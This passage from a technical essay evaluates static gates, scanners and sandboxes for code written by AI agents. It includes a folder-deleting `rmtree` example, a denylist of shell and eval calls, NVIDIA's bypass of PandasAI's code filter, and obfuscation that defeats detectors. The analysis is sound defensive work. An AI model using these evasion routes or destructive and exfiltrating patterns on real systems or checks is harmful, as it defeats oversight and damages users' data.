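None of these figures is a block rate for malicious code. The detector's rules cover insecure coding practices, and its test had no category for programs that steal or destroy data on purpose. Bhatt and colleagues point out that code alone is neither malicious nor benign. For example, a script that encrypts a home directory could protect the owner's files or hold them to ransom. To measure whether models help with cyberattacks, they therefore wrote openly malicious requests and had a second language model judge the answers, instead of using the detector.

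### Scanners tested on malicious packages

The best evidence on deliberately malicious code comes from package registries. Guo and colleagues ran 11 detectors with default settings on the npm benchmark described earlier, whose benign samples are popular packages. The table shows six of the results. The false-block rates are calculated from the published precision and the number of samples.

| Tool | How it decides | Block rate | False-block rate |
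|---|---|---|---|
| Packj, static mode | flags any use of 56 sensitive functions | 98.7% | 85.5% |
| OSSGadget | searches all files for text patterns | 91.6% | 79.3% |
| GuardDog | Semgrep rules, data-flow tracking and package metadata | 89.9% | 2.5% |
| GENIE | strict data-flow queries in CodeQL | 46.1% | 0.1% |
| SocketAI | a language model reads the code and reviews its own verdict | 44.4% | 0.7% |
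| IntelGuard | a language model compares the code with known malware | 93.8% | 1.5% |

Malicious and harmless packages call the same functions. A build script and a backdoor may both start a shell, for example. Packj flags packages for calling these functions, so it flags most legitimate packages. OSSGadget raises additional false alarms by matching words such as `curl` in comments and documentation. GENIE's queries are much narrower. One requires at least three different pieces of system information to reach the same web request, so it misses a program that sends only one.

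GuardDog strikes a much better balance because it tracks data from sensitive sources to the network and exempts known legitimate install scripts. It also takes only 2.55 seconds to scan a package of about 3,000 lines, compared with 146 seconds for SocketAI. But its result may be slightly too favourable, because GuardDog was used to help find some of the malware and check the labels.

IntelGuard and SocketAI ran on the same language model, so the difference of 49 percentage points comes from how they used it. Before classifying code, IntelGuard retrieves similar examples from more than 8,000 reports on known threats. Some of those reports may describe packages in the benchmark, which would make IntelGuard's score a less reliable estimate of its performance on new malware.

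#### Combining tools and testing them over time

Running two scanners and blocking whatever either one flags can add more false alarms than detections. When Guo and colleagues combined GuardDog with Packj, Packj caught 665 malicious packages that GuardDog had missed but added 6,015 false alarms, and precision fell from 97% to 50%. GuardDog combined with IntelGuard blocked 97.4% of malicious packages with 96.0% precision, because both tools raise few false alarms and they miss different packages. A builder who adds Semgrep to Bandit should count new detections and new false alarms in the same way.

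A tool's block rate can also change when its rules don't. The study ran the same version of each tool on malware from different years, and GENIE's block rate varied between 3.8% and 72.2%, depending on whether that period's attacks fit its queries. GuardDog's block rate recovered after a weaker period and reached 91.4% on malware from 2024 and 2025. Guo and colleagues credit the recovery to rule updates, but a test of a single version can't separate the effect of updates from the effect of changes in the malware. Attacks through install scripts, which GuardDog detects well, also became more common in those years.

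#### A second comparison

*MalTotal* (2026) presents a new detector and compares it with existing ones on packages in several languages. On JavaScript, GuardDog blocked 84.3% of the malicious packages with a precision of 75.9%, and OSSGadget blocked 66.8%. Both block rates are lower than in the npm study, OSSGadget's by almost 25 points. Both studies counted a single GuardDog alert as a detection, so most of the difference in GuardDog's results probably comes from the samples. On Python, GuardDog blocked 92.9% of the malicious packages with a precision of 92.4%.

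Even a good false-block rate can be too high for a registry. In *One Detector Fits All* (2025), a detector tuned to a false-alarm rate of 0.1% checked 91,949 PyPI packages over 37 days. It found about 2.5 malicious packages and raised two false alarms a day on average. At the 2.5% rate GuardDog had in the npm study, that many packages would have caused about 60 false alarms a day, although newly published packages may trigger GuardDog's rules less often than popular ones do.

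### How far package results apply to an agent's scripts

The largest difference between npm packages and an agent's scripts is how the code starts. npm runs a package's install scripts automatically, and 72% of the malicious packages in the npm benchmark use them for the attack. Two of GuardDog's 22 rules, one for suspicious install scripts and one for suspicious web addresses, account for more than 90% of its detections. The web-address rule could also work on a script for analysing sales files, but the install-script rule would have nothing to examine. Guo and colleagues don't report GuardDog's block rate without the install-script rule, so their results don't show how it would perform on an agent's scripts.

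GuardDog caught more than 94% of the malicious packages that send data out or run shell commands, but only 7% of those that build and execute code at run time. The high figures may overstate how well it detects those behaviours, because they are rates for whole packages. A package that steals data probably counts as a detected theft even if GuardDog flags only its install script.

Data theft is common in both settings, but the data differ. Malicious packages typically collect the machine's name, the user name and network details, because their authors don't know whose computer they will reach. A hijacked agent may already have the location of the file that holds the sales figures or the passwords. The benchmark's 11 types of behaviour don't include destroying the user's files, which is one of the main risks for an agent. The nearest category covers writing a payload to the disk and deleting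 evidence. A high score on packages is therefore some evidence that a scanner will catch data theft by an agent, but very little evidence that it will catch file deletion.

Malicious npm packages are becoming more like an agent's scripts in that they make fewer calls to sensitive functions. The average fell from 12.5 calls per package in 2021 to 6.8 in 2023. In 2024 and 2025, 12.6% of the malware made only one or two such calls, and about half of these packages only ran a single shell command. Such code is hard for a data-flow rule to catch because, if the command itself contacts the attacker's server, the program has no web request of its own that the rule could treat as an outlet.

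The benign samples differ too. *MalGuard* (2025), which describes another detector for Python packages, found that OSSGadget and Bandit4Mal often mistake ordinary network connections and file operations for malicious ones. An agent that reads sales files and downloads exchange rates routinely does both. Skills are closer to an agent's scripts than packages are, and on the SkillGate benchmark a scanner without a language model had no usable threshold.

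Bandit4Mal, a fork of Bandit with added patterns for malicious code, is probably the tool in these comparisons most similar to a simple gate for Python scripts. In the *MalTotal* comparison, it flagged 18.6% of the malicious Python packages, and only 38.8% of the packages it flagged were malicious. The comparison counted only findings with both high severity and high confidence, so a lower threshold might have caught more malicious packages.

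## What static checks cannot see, and what to put behind them

Better rules would prevent some of the misses in these tests, but a gate that only reads programs has other limits that no rule can remove. Some are mathematical, and others exist because the harmful step may not be in the program's text.

### Why no detector is always right

Henry Gordon Rice proved in his 1951 dissertation that no algorithm can answer a question about a program's behavior correctly for every program, unless the answer is the same for all of them.

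Suppose a function `deletes_report` takes any program and always answers correctly whether running it would delete the user's report folder. Now take any calculation `P` that touches no files, and put a deletion after it:

```python
import shutil
P()
shutil.rmtree("/home/ana/report")
```

The program deletes the folder if `P` finishes, and never reaches the last line if `P` runs forever. We could therefore use `deletes_report` to determine whether any program `P` finishes, which would solve the halting problem. No algorithm can do that, so `deletes_report` can't exist. The same argument works with an upload or any other harm on the last line.

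A time limit makes the question answerable, because a tester can run the program for ten seconds and see whether it deletes the folder in that time. This doesn't help a static gate much, since a static gate checks code without running it, and the result holds only for the files and settings the program had during the run.

A gate can stop every deletion by refusing every program that it can't show to be harmless, although the proof shows that no gate can always be right. It would refuse the program above because the text contains a call to `rmtree`, without working out whether `P` finishes. A parser can check any program for a certain call because the check depends only on syntax. But this is stricter than checking whether the program would actually delete anything, so the gate also blocks some harmless programs, such as the one above when `P` runs forever.

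A gate that catches every harmful program must therefore refuse some harmless ones. But we can't infer from the theorem how many of those an agent would write, and an agent with a narrow job may write hardly any.

This strategy works only if the gate treats "unknown" as a reason to stop. Jing's gate for shell commands marks pipelines and several other constructs as undecidable instead of guessing what they do. Of the 216 commands from the older Windows study, it marked 15 this way. An early version allowed commands with syntax errors, because the gate received an empty list of arguments and found no target to block. Jing changed the gate to refuse these commands, and over the series of changes that included this fix, wrong approvals among the 216 commands fell from 42 to 30.

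### Where the harmful step hides

Python lets a program fetch a function by a name that it works out while running. Honest programs do this too:

```python
choice = settings["average"]        # "mean" or "median"
print(getattr(statistics, choice)(amounts))
```

When a program reads a function's name from a settings file, the syntax tree shows the call but not which function is called. A hostile program can use the same feature to call a forbidden function whose name appears nowhere in its text. Searching for the name as a string doesn't help, because the program can assemble the string from pieces. The tree does show that the program looks up a function by a name set at run time, so a gate can reject the lookup, whichever function it would return.

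A permitted library can also give code access to a forbidden function. NVIDIA's testers got past the filter in PandasAI partly by calling functions from untrusted libraries that the trusted ones had imported. Such flaws can take a long time to fix. An outside researcher reported a first problem in April 2023. NVIDIA reported more in June 2024, and the maintainers released a fix in July. On 20 November 2024 the maintainers confirmed that the fix stopped the attack NVIDIA had demonstrated, but five days later NVIDIA sent them a new version of the attack that still got past the filter.

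Sometimes a program contains no harmful instructions when the gate checks it because they arrive later. The program may download text and execute it, load a file in a format that can carry code, or install a package. The gate can then examine only the code that does the loading. Malware writers have long distributed their programs in a compressed or encrypted form that unpacks itself at run time. Roundy and Miller's *Hybrid Analysis and Control of Malware* lists this as one of the three most common obstacles to analysis, along with code that overwrites itself and disguised jumps from one part of a program to another.

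In Python source, the step that turns data into running code is usually visible, for example as a call to `exec`, so a gate can refuse it. Refusing it is harder when the step is part of the agent's normal work. The sales agent may have a good reason to install a charting library, but the gate hasn't checked the library's code.

In other programs every instruction is visible, but the harm depends on the input or the machine. One line in a settings file determines whether the script that clears a temporary folder is harmless or disastrous. Pourleyli and colleagues found that weaknesses that exhaust a machine's resources often became apparent only during execution, as excessive memory use or a calculation that never ended. A static analyser can examine a branch that a trial run would rarely take, but it often can't tell whether that branch can ever run. If it rejects a program whenever it can't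 tell, it will also reject programs whose dangerous branch can never run.

Finally, the harm can be spread over several programs. Suppose one script copies the stored passwords into the report folder, and another backs up that folder to an outside server the next day. The data-flow rule described earlier lets both through, because neither script both opens a password file and sends data out. To connect them, the gate would have to keep a record of which files contain secrets, across programs and for as long as the files exist.

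This kind of memory is difficult even within one script. Jing's gate splits a sequence of commands, judges each one, and refuses the whole sequence if it would deny any of them. That is enough to stop an attack that hides a forbidden command behind a harmless one. Six of the commands from the Windows study had a second action on a new line, and the gate denied four of them. But the gate doesn't carry the effects of one command over to the next, so it can misjudge a command whose meaning depends on what an earlier one changed.

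### Disguised code

All of these cases can occur in benign code, whereas obfuscation is meant to make a program hard to read. *Limits of Static Analysis for Malware Detection* (Moser, Kruegel and Kirda, 2007) tested how well obfuscation could evade the best detectors of the time.

At the time, virus scanners mostly searched for known byte sequences, so rewriting a program easily defeated them. Researchers had therefore built detectors that looked for behaviour. One of them searched for programs that look up their own file name and then copy that file elsewhere, as a worm does. It still detected them after variables were renamed or useless instructions were inserted.

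Moser and colleagues wrote a tool that rewrites compiled programs using *opaque constants*, pieces of code that always produce the same number but make that number hard for an analyser to determine. If the number is the destination of a jump or the address of a variable, the analyser can't tell where the program goes next or what data it uses. In one version, finding the exact number means solving a logic problem called 3SAT. Unlike the halting problem, 3SAT is solvable, but every known method can take impractically long on large instances.

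They applied the tool to three worms (two variants of MyDoom and one of Klez) and checked that the worms still worked. Every detector had recognised all three before the rewriting.

| Detector | Rewritten worms it still recognised |
|---|---|
| Kaspersky | 0 of 3 |
| Ikarus | 0 of 3 |
| McAfee | 2 of 3 |
| AntiVir | 2 of 3 |
| Behaviour-based detector | 0 of 3 |

McAfee and AntiVir still detected two worms because they also matched bytes in the programs' stored data, which the tool had not changed. Changing those bytes ended the detection. The behaviour-based detector failed because it could no longer follow the jumps, identify the calls to the operating system, or confirm that the copied file was the one whose name the program had requested.

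The disguise had only minor drawbacks for an attacker. With the simpler constants, programs grew by 237% on average, and calculation-heavy ones took about 50% longer to run. Of 774 ordinary Linux programs put through the tool, eleven crashed.

Three worms are enough to prove that such an evasion is possible, but not to show how often attackers use it. Moser and colleagues wrote that nobody had yet encountered these techniques in real malware. Many attackers still don't disguise their code, as the npm benchmark described earlier shows. A gate can therefore block most samples in such a collection and still give almost no protection against an attacker who does.

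Later researchers reached similar conclusions about more advanced methods. In *On the Limits of Information Flow Techniques for Malware Analysis and Containment*, Cavallaro, Saxena and Sekar argue that tracking data through a program is quite robust for detecting attacks on honest software, but runs into several difficulties when the software may be malicious. Unlike an honest programmer, a malicious one has a reason to break the trail between a password and a network request. Roundy and Miller analyse the code before it runs, then monitor selected parts of the execution and use what they learn to extend the analysis.

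A gate could treat signs of obfuscation as suspicious in themselves. Moser and colleagues warn that this causes false alarms, because companies also obfuscate legitimate software to protect their intellectual property. That objection is serious for a virus scanner but much weaker for a gate on an agent's scripts. A script that draws a sales chart contains no trade secrets to protect, and the agent can rewrite it in plain form if the gate rejects it. Some harmless scripts do contain encoded data, such as an image embedded as a long string, so the rule should look for encoded data that the program executes.

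### A gate for a trapped-ion laboratory

Some of these limits disappear if the gate can do a trial run of the program. Wang, Qi and colleagues built such a gate for a physics laboratory and then attacked it themselves (*A hardware-safety-gated system for LLM-written native ARTIQ control code*, 2026).

The laboratory holds single charged atoms in place with electric fields and manipulates them with laser pulses. An agent based on Claude Opus 4.8 writes Python scripts that set the frequencies, voltages and pulses. A wrong value can damage the equipment. The agent has no direct connection to the hardware, and each of its scripts goes through these steps:

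1. A checker walks the syntax tree and refuses the script if it finds a call or import on a denylist, such as `os.system`, `subprocess` or `eval`.
2. A separate computer runs the script in a simulator, where software models replace the real devices, and records every hardware operation.
3. The filter compares each operation with limits that a person has set for each device. A value outside the limits blocks the script.
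4. If everything is within the limits, the filter issues a token for this one call with exactly these contents. The hardware software accepts no call without a token.

If the simulation can't reach a definite result, for example because its computer is down, the filter blocks the script and passes it to a person. Scripts that operate the oxygen valve always fail the review, and the designers gave the agent no interface to the oven that supplies the atoms.

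#### What the attacks found

The filter is meant for an agent that makes mistakes or reads misleading text, not for a determined attacker. It was still tested to find its limits, using 1,932 scripts, some written by a language model and some by hand, each with a predicted result. About 250 further tests attacked token handling and other internal interfaces. Nobody managed to use a token twice or for a different call.

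The scripts included 631 calibration programs like those the agent normally writes, and the filter approved all of them. The study divides the other 1,301 into requests the filter blocked, approvals at the edge of its protection, and scripts the simulator couldn't evaluate because they weren't valid control programs.

The filter rejected every script that commanded a declared device beyond its limit, including those that reached the forbidden value gradually in a loop or by replaying a recorded sequence of pulses. The forbidden number may not appear anywhere in the text of such a script, so a syntax check would have to do the whole program's arithmetic to find it, whereas the simulator records the result.

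Zero false rejections in 631 scripts gives an upper limit of 0.58% on the false-block rate, if the scripts are independent. The scripts cover only a few types of calibration, so the true limit is less certain. Wang and colleagues attribute the result to the absence of any language model or other source of chance in the decision. That makes the verdicts repeatable, but a fixed rule can still be wrong every time. A more likely reason is that ordinary calibrations stay well within the limits and use simple code.

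QLab's *Can large language models (LLMs) safely run quantum experiments?*, a summary by one of the laboratories involved, states that the filter correctly blocked every unsafe or disallowed request. This shouldn't be read as a block rate of 100%, because the study counts the approvals at the edge of the filter's protection separately. They fall into seven categories:

| Gap | Why the filter approves the script | What has to close the gap |
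|---|---|---|
| Undeclared devices | It applies limits only to devices in the operator's configuration | The configuration |
| Values left over from an earlier experiment | It judges only what the script itself commands | The review of the earlier script |
| Missing or wrong limits | It uses the limits that the operator wrote | The configuration |
| Old approvals | A stored approval remains valid after someone tightens a limit | The operator, by deleting it |
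| Forbidden operations in an unfamiliar form | The denylist doesn't contain that form | A stricter syntax check |
| Differences between simulator and hardware | The device models lack some advanced features | Better models |
| Another way to run files | A scan of the script folder can run a file before its review | A change to the software |

Wang and colleagues regard only the last three as weaknesses and describe the first four as deliberate divisions of responsibility between the filter and the operator. That describes the design fairly, but the damage to the equipment is the same either way. For example, several lasers can each stay within their limits and still deliver too much power together if nobody has written a limit for the total.

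The paper also contradicts itself about undeclared devices. According to its description of the design, the filter blocks a script that uses such a device and refers it to a person, but according to its list of gaps, the script passes. Anyone who copies the design should test this case first.

#### Why measurements defeat both stages

Some experiments choose their next step based on a measurement. For instance, a script might count the photons an atom emits and fire another laser pulse only if it counts enough. The simulator has no real atom, so its model of the detector always returns zero, and only the branch for a dark atom runs. If the other branch sets the laser power too high, the simulator's record won't show it.

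The syntax check examines both branches, but it has no values to compare with the limits. It can recognise a condition that directly uses the detector's result and reject the script, though it may miss the same condition if the result first passes through other variables.

Simulating every branch doesn't work in general, because *n* measurements with two possible outcomes each can produce up to 2ⁿ paths, which is more than a million for 20 measurements. If a measurement also determines how often a loop repeats, the number of paths isn't fixed in advance. Because of the halting problem, nobody can guarantee in general that such a loop ends.

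The filter therefore approves only scripts whose hardware operations don't depend on measurements. This restricted this laboratory little, because its calibrations fix the whole sequence of pulses before the first measurement. An agent that had to correct errors during an experiment couldn't work under this rule.

Rehearsing an ordinary script has the same problem. A simulated web server, for example, returns only the responses its author thought of.

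### Refusing more constructs

Wang and colleagues found that every device command in the 631 calibration scripts they tested named the device's method directly. Every attack that got past the filter used at least one indirect form, such as an alias, a chain of helper functions or an unusual import. They therefore want to replace the denylist with an allowlist that contains only the constructs found in ordinary calibrations.

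On the recorded scripts, this would separate attacks from legitimate work perfectly. But a rule derived from a set of scripts will always fit that set well, as *STELP*'s configuration fitted its benchmark. Aliases and helper functions are also normal in good code, so the agent would probably violate the new rule as its programs got longer. Wang and colleagues say they need a long record of normal operation to estimate how often this would happen. They describe the change as making the gate err by rejecting unfamiliar code instead of by accepting unsafe code.

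The price of refusing a dynamic construct depends on how easily the agent can do without it. The program that chooses between mean and median needs only an ordinary condition:

```python
if settings["average"] == "median":
    print(statistics.median(amounts))
else:
    print(statistics.mean(amounts))
```

A gate can analyze this version completely. Other programs are harder to rewrite, as the earlier feedback experiment showed for `eval`. A builder can make rewriting easier by offering a safe replacement for common uses of a blocked feature and naming it in the rejection message.

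Refusing dynamic code doesn't help against harm that depends on input, or harm spread over several programs, because those programs may contain nothing dynamic.

### Rehearsing a script on a copy

The laboratory could simulate its scripts because a simulator for its control system already existed. Wang and colleagues expect that building a simulator of similar quality would be the main work in moving the filter to another control system.

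For scripts that work with files, a copy of the folder can replace the simulator. The system copies `/home/ana/report`, runs the script on the copy and compares the folder before and after. If the whole report is gone, it asks the user. Unlike the simulated detector, the copy contains the real data, so the script takes the branch it would take on the original at that moment.

If the changes from this run look right, the system can then copy them back to the real folder instead of running the script again. The script runs only once, so the trial and the real run can't differ. This doesn't work for actions that take effect immediately, such as a laser pulse or a web request.

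Comparing a folder before and after a run also has limits. In Jing's experiments, the comparison couldn't correctly attribute disk changes in 3 of 117 runs (2.6%). This can happen when a program creates a file and links it to another name during the same run, because the file isn't in the earlier snapshot. The method also takes time and disk space, and it can't detect that a script has sent files elsewhere.

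### NVIDIA's case for isolation

NVIDIA draws a more radical conclusion from the PandasAI case and calls isolation mandatory for any system that runs generated code. It argues that a filter's developers have to anticipate every way untrusted code could do harm, while an attacker needs to find only one they missed. Fixing one bypass leaves the others open. A sandbox limits what the program can reach however it is written, so developers don't have to anticipate each attack.

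NVIDIA still recommends filters as an additional defence that stops opportunistic attacks, but it says that relying on them alone creates "a false sense of security".

NVIDIA's evidence comes from a single product, PandasAI, and the company has some interest in the conclusion because it has its own toolkit for running agents' code in sandboxes. But the argument follows from the limits described above, however good PandasAI's filter was, and the trapped-ion study reached much the same conclusion about its own denylist. NVIDIA goes too far only when it calls the sandbox the one reliable boundary. Sandboxes have had flaws too, and even a flawless one would permit the kinds of harm discussed in the next sections.

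#### A sandbox without network or secrets

How much a sandbox protects depends on what is inside it. Each run of the sales agent could get a new virtual machine with a read-only copy of the sales files, an empty folder for results, and limits on time and memory. The machine would have no passwords or network connection.

`send.py` fails twice in this environment, because the password file doesn't exist and the server isn't reachable. It fails whether it names its functions openly, assembles them at run time or hides them behind an unsolvable puzzle. This is the environment's main advantage over the gate, whose result depends on how the functions are written.

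The main drawback of blocking network access is that some legitimate programs fail too. For example, an agent can't download current exchange rates. A process outside the sandbox can fetch the rates and put them in a file, or the sandbox can allow connections to one address. Data could leak through any allowed address, so the list should be short. Libraries have to be in the machine's image beforehand, since the script can't install them.

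The sandbox also doesn't control what happens to the results. The sales figures have to be inside the sandbox, and the program may print them. The agent may then pass them on with another tool, so a check on the agent's other tools has to cover that step.

NVIDIA's *Sandboxing Agentic AI Workflows with WebAssembly* describes isolation in small virtual machines, such as Firecracker, as demanding in both computing resources and engineering. It proposes running the code in the user's browser instead, using Pyodide, a version of Python compiled to WebAssembly. Browsers execute WebAssembly in their own sandbox. The server sends the generated script to the browser in a web page, and the browser runs it to draw a chart. This keeps a harmful script from running on the server, where it could affect other users.

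This suits an agent that draws charts, but not one that has to work with files on the server. Many Python packages work in Pyodide, but a program can fail if it needs one that doesn't. A web page can usually send requests to other servers, so the page needs its own restrictions if the chart contains confidential figures. NVIDIA doesn't report how many attacks this stops or how many ordinary scripts fail.

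### What the gate still contributes

A static gate is still useful alongside a sandbox, even though the sandbox works whatever the code looks like. The gate is fast enough to check every program, so slower methods are needed only for the programs it flags as doubtful. It also acts before a program runs, whereas a sandbox may stop a program halfway, after it has changed half of the files it was allowed to change.

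A gate can also return the reason for its decision. *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) describes a system in which small fixed rules check each tool call against a written policy and the current contents of a database. If a rule rejects the call, the agent gets a structured message with the reason instead of the result, and can make a new plan. A sandbox returns only the error caused by the missing permission. In NVIDIA's browser example, a script that tries to load an attack library stops because Python can't find the module. An agent could easily mistake this for an installation problem and try to fix it.

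The explanation has to be correct to be useful. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* cites findings that most analysers give little context for their warnings, and that Semgrep and CodeQL results often differ from experts' judgements of code written by language models. If a gate refuses a program because the program couldn't be analysed, the message should give that as the reason. Jing's gate does this, so the agent can respond by writing simpler code and doesn't mistake the refusal for a detected attack.

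The strongest reason to keep the gate is that the sandbox has to permit some harmful actions. An agent that edits the user's report needs write access to the report folder, and that access also lets it empty the folder. This is why the AppArmor profile in Jing's experiment let through harmful effects that the gate stopped. The rules in *Reason Less, Verify More* address a similar problem. One checks whether a customer's booking is eligible for cancellation. No sandbox could make this check, because permitted and forbidden cancellations use the same tool.

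Multiplying the miss rates of the gate and the sandbox gives the right combined rate only if the two fail on unrelated programs, and they often fail on the same ones. If the gate misses 6% of malicious programs and the sandbox fails to contain 10%, multiplying gives a combined miss rate of 0.6%. But in the invented test of the sales agent's gate, all 12 misses were programs that delete or overwrite the user's files. A sandbox that gives the agent write access to those files contains none of the 12, so the combined miss rate is still 6%. The two layers need to be tested together on the same samples, with the programs running in the sandbox and the results broken down by harm.

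For the sales agent, such a test would probably show that theft is well covered and deletion isn't:

| Program | Gate | Sandbox without network or secrets | Working on a copy |
|---|---|---|---|
| `send.py` | refuses it | nothing to steal, nowhere to send it | no help |
| The same theft with names assembled at run time | refuses it only if it refuses unknown calls | nothing to steal, nowhere to send it | no help |
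| Deletes the report instead of the temporary folder | can only ask, unless it knows which folders to protect | permits it | the user can reject the change |
| Calculates the average of the wrong column | allows it | permits it | no help |

The third program needs the copy, because neither the gate nor the sandbox can distinguish it from the correct script. Nothing in the table stops the fourth program. Its code breaks none of the rules used here, and only someone who knows what the user asked for can find the mistake.
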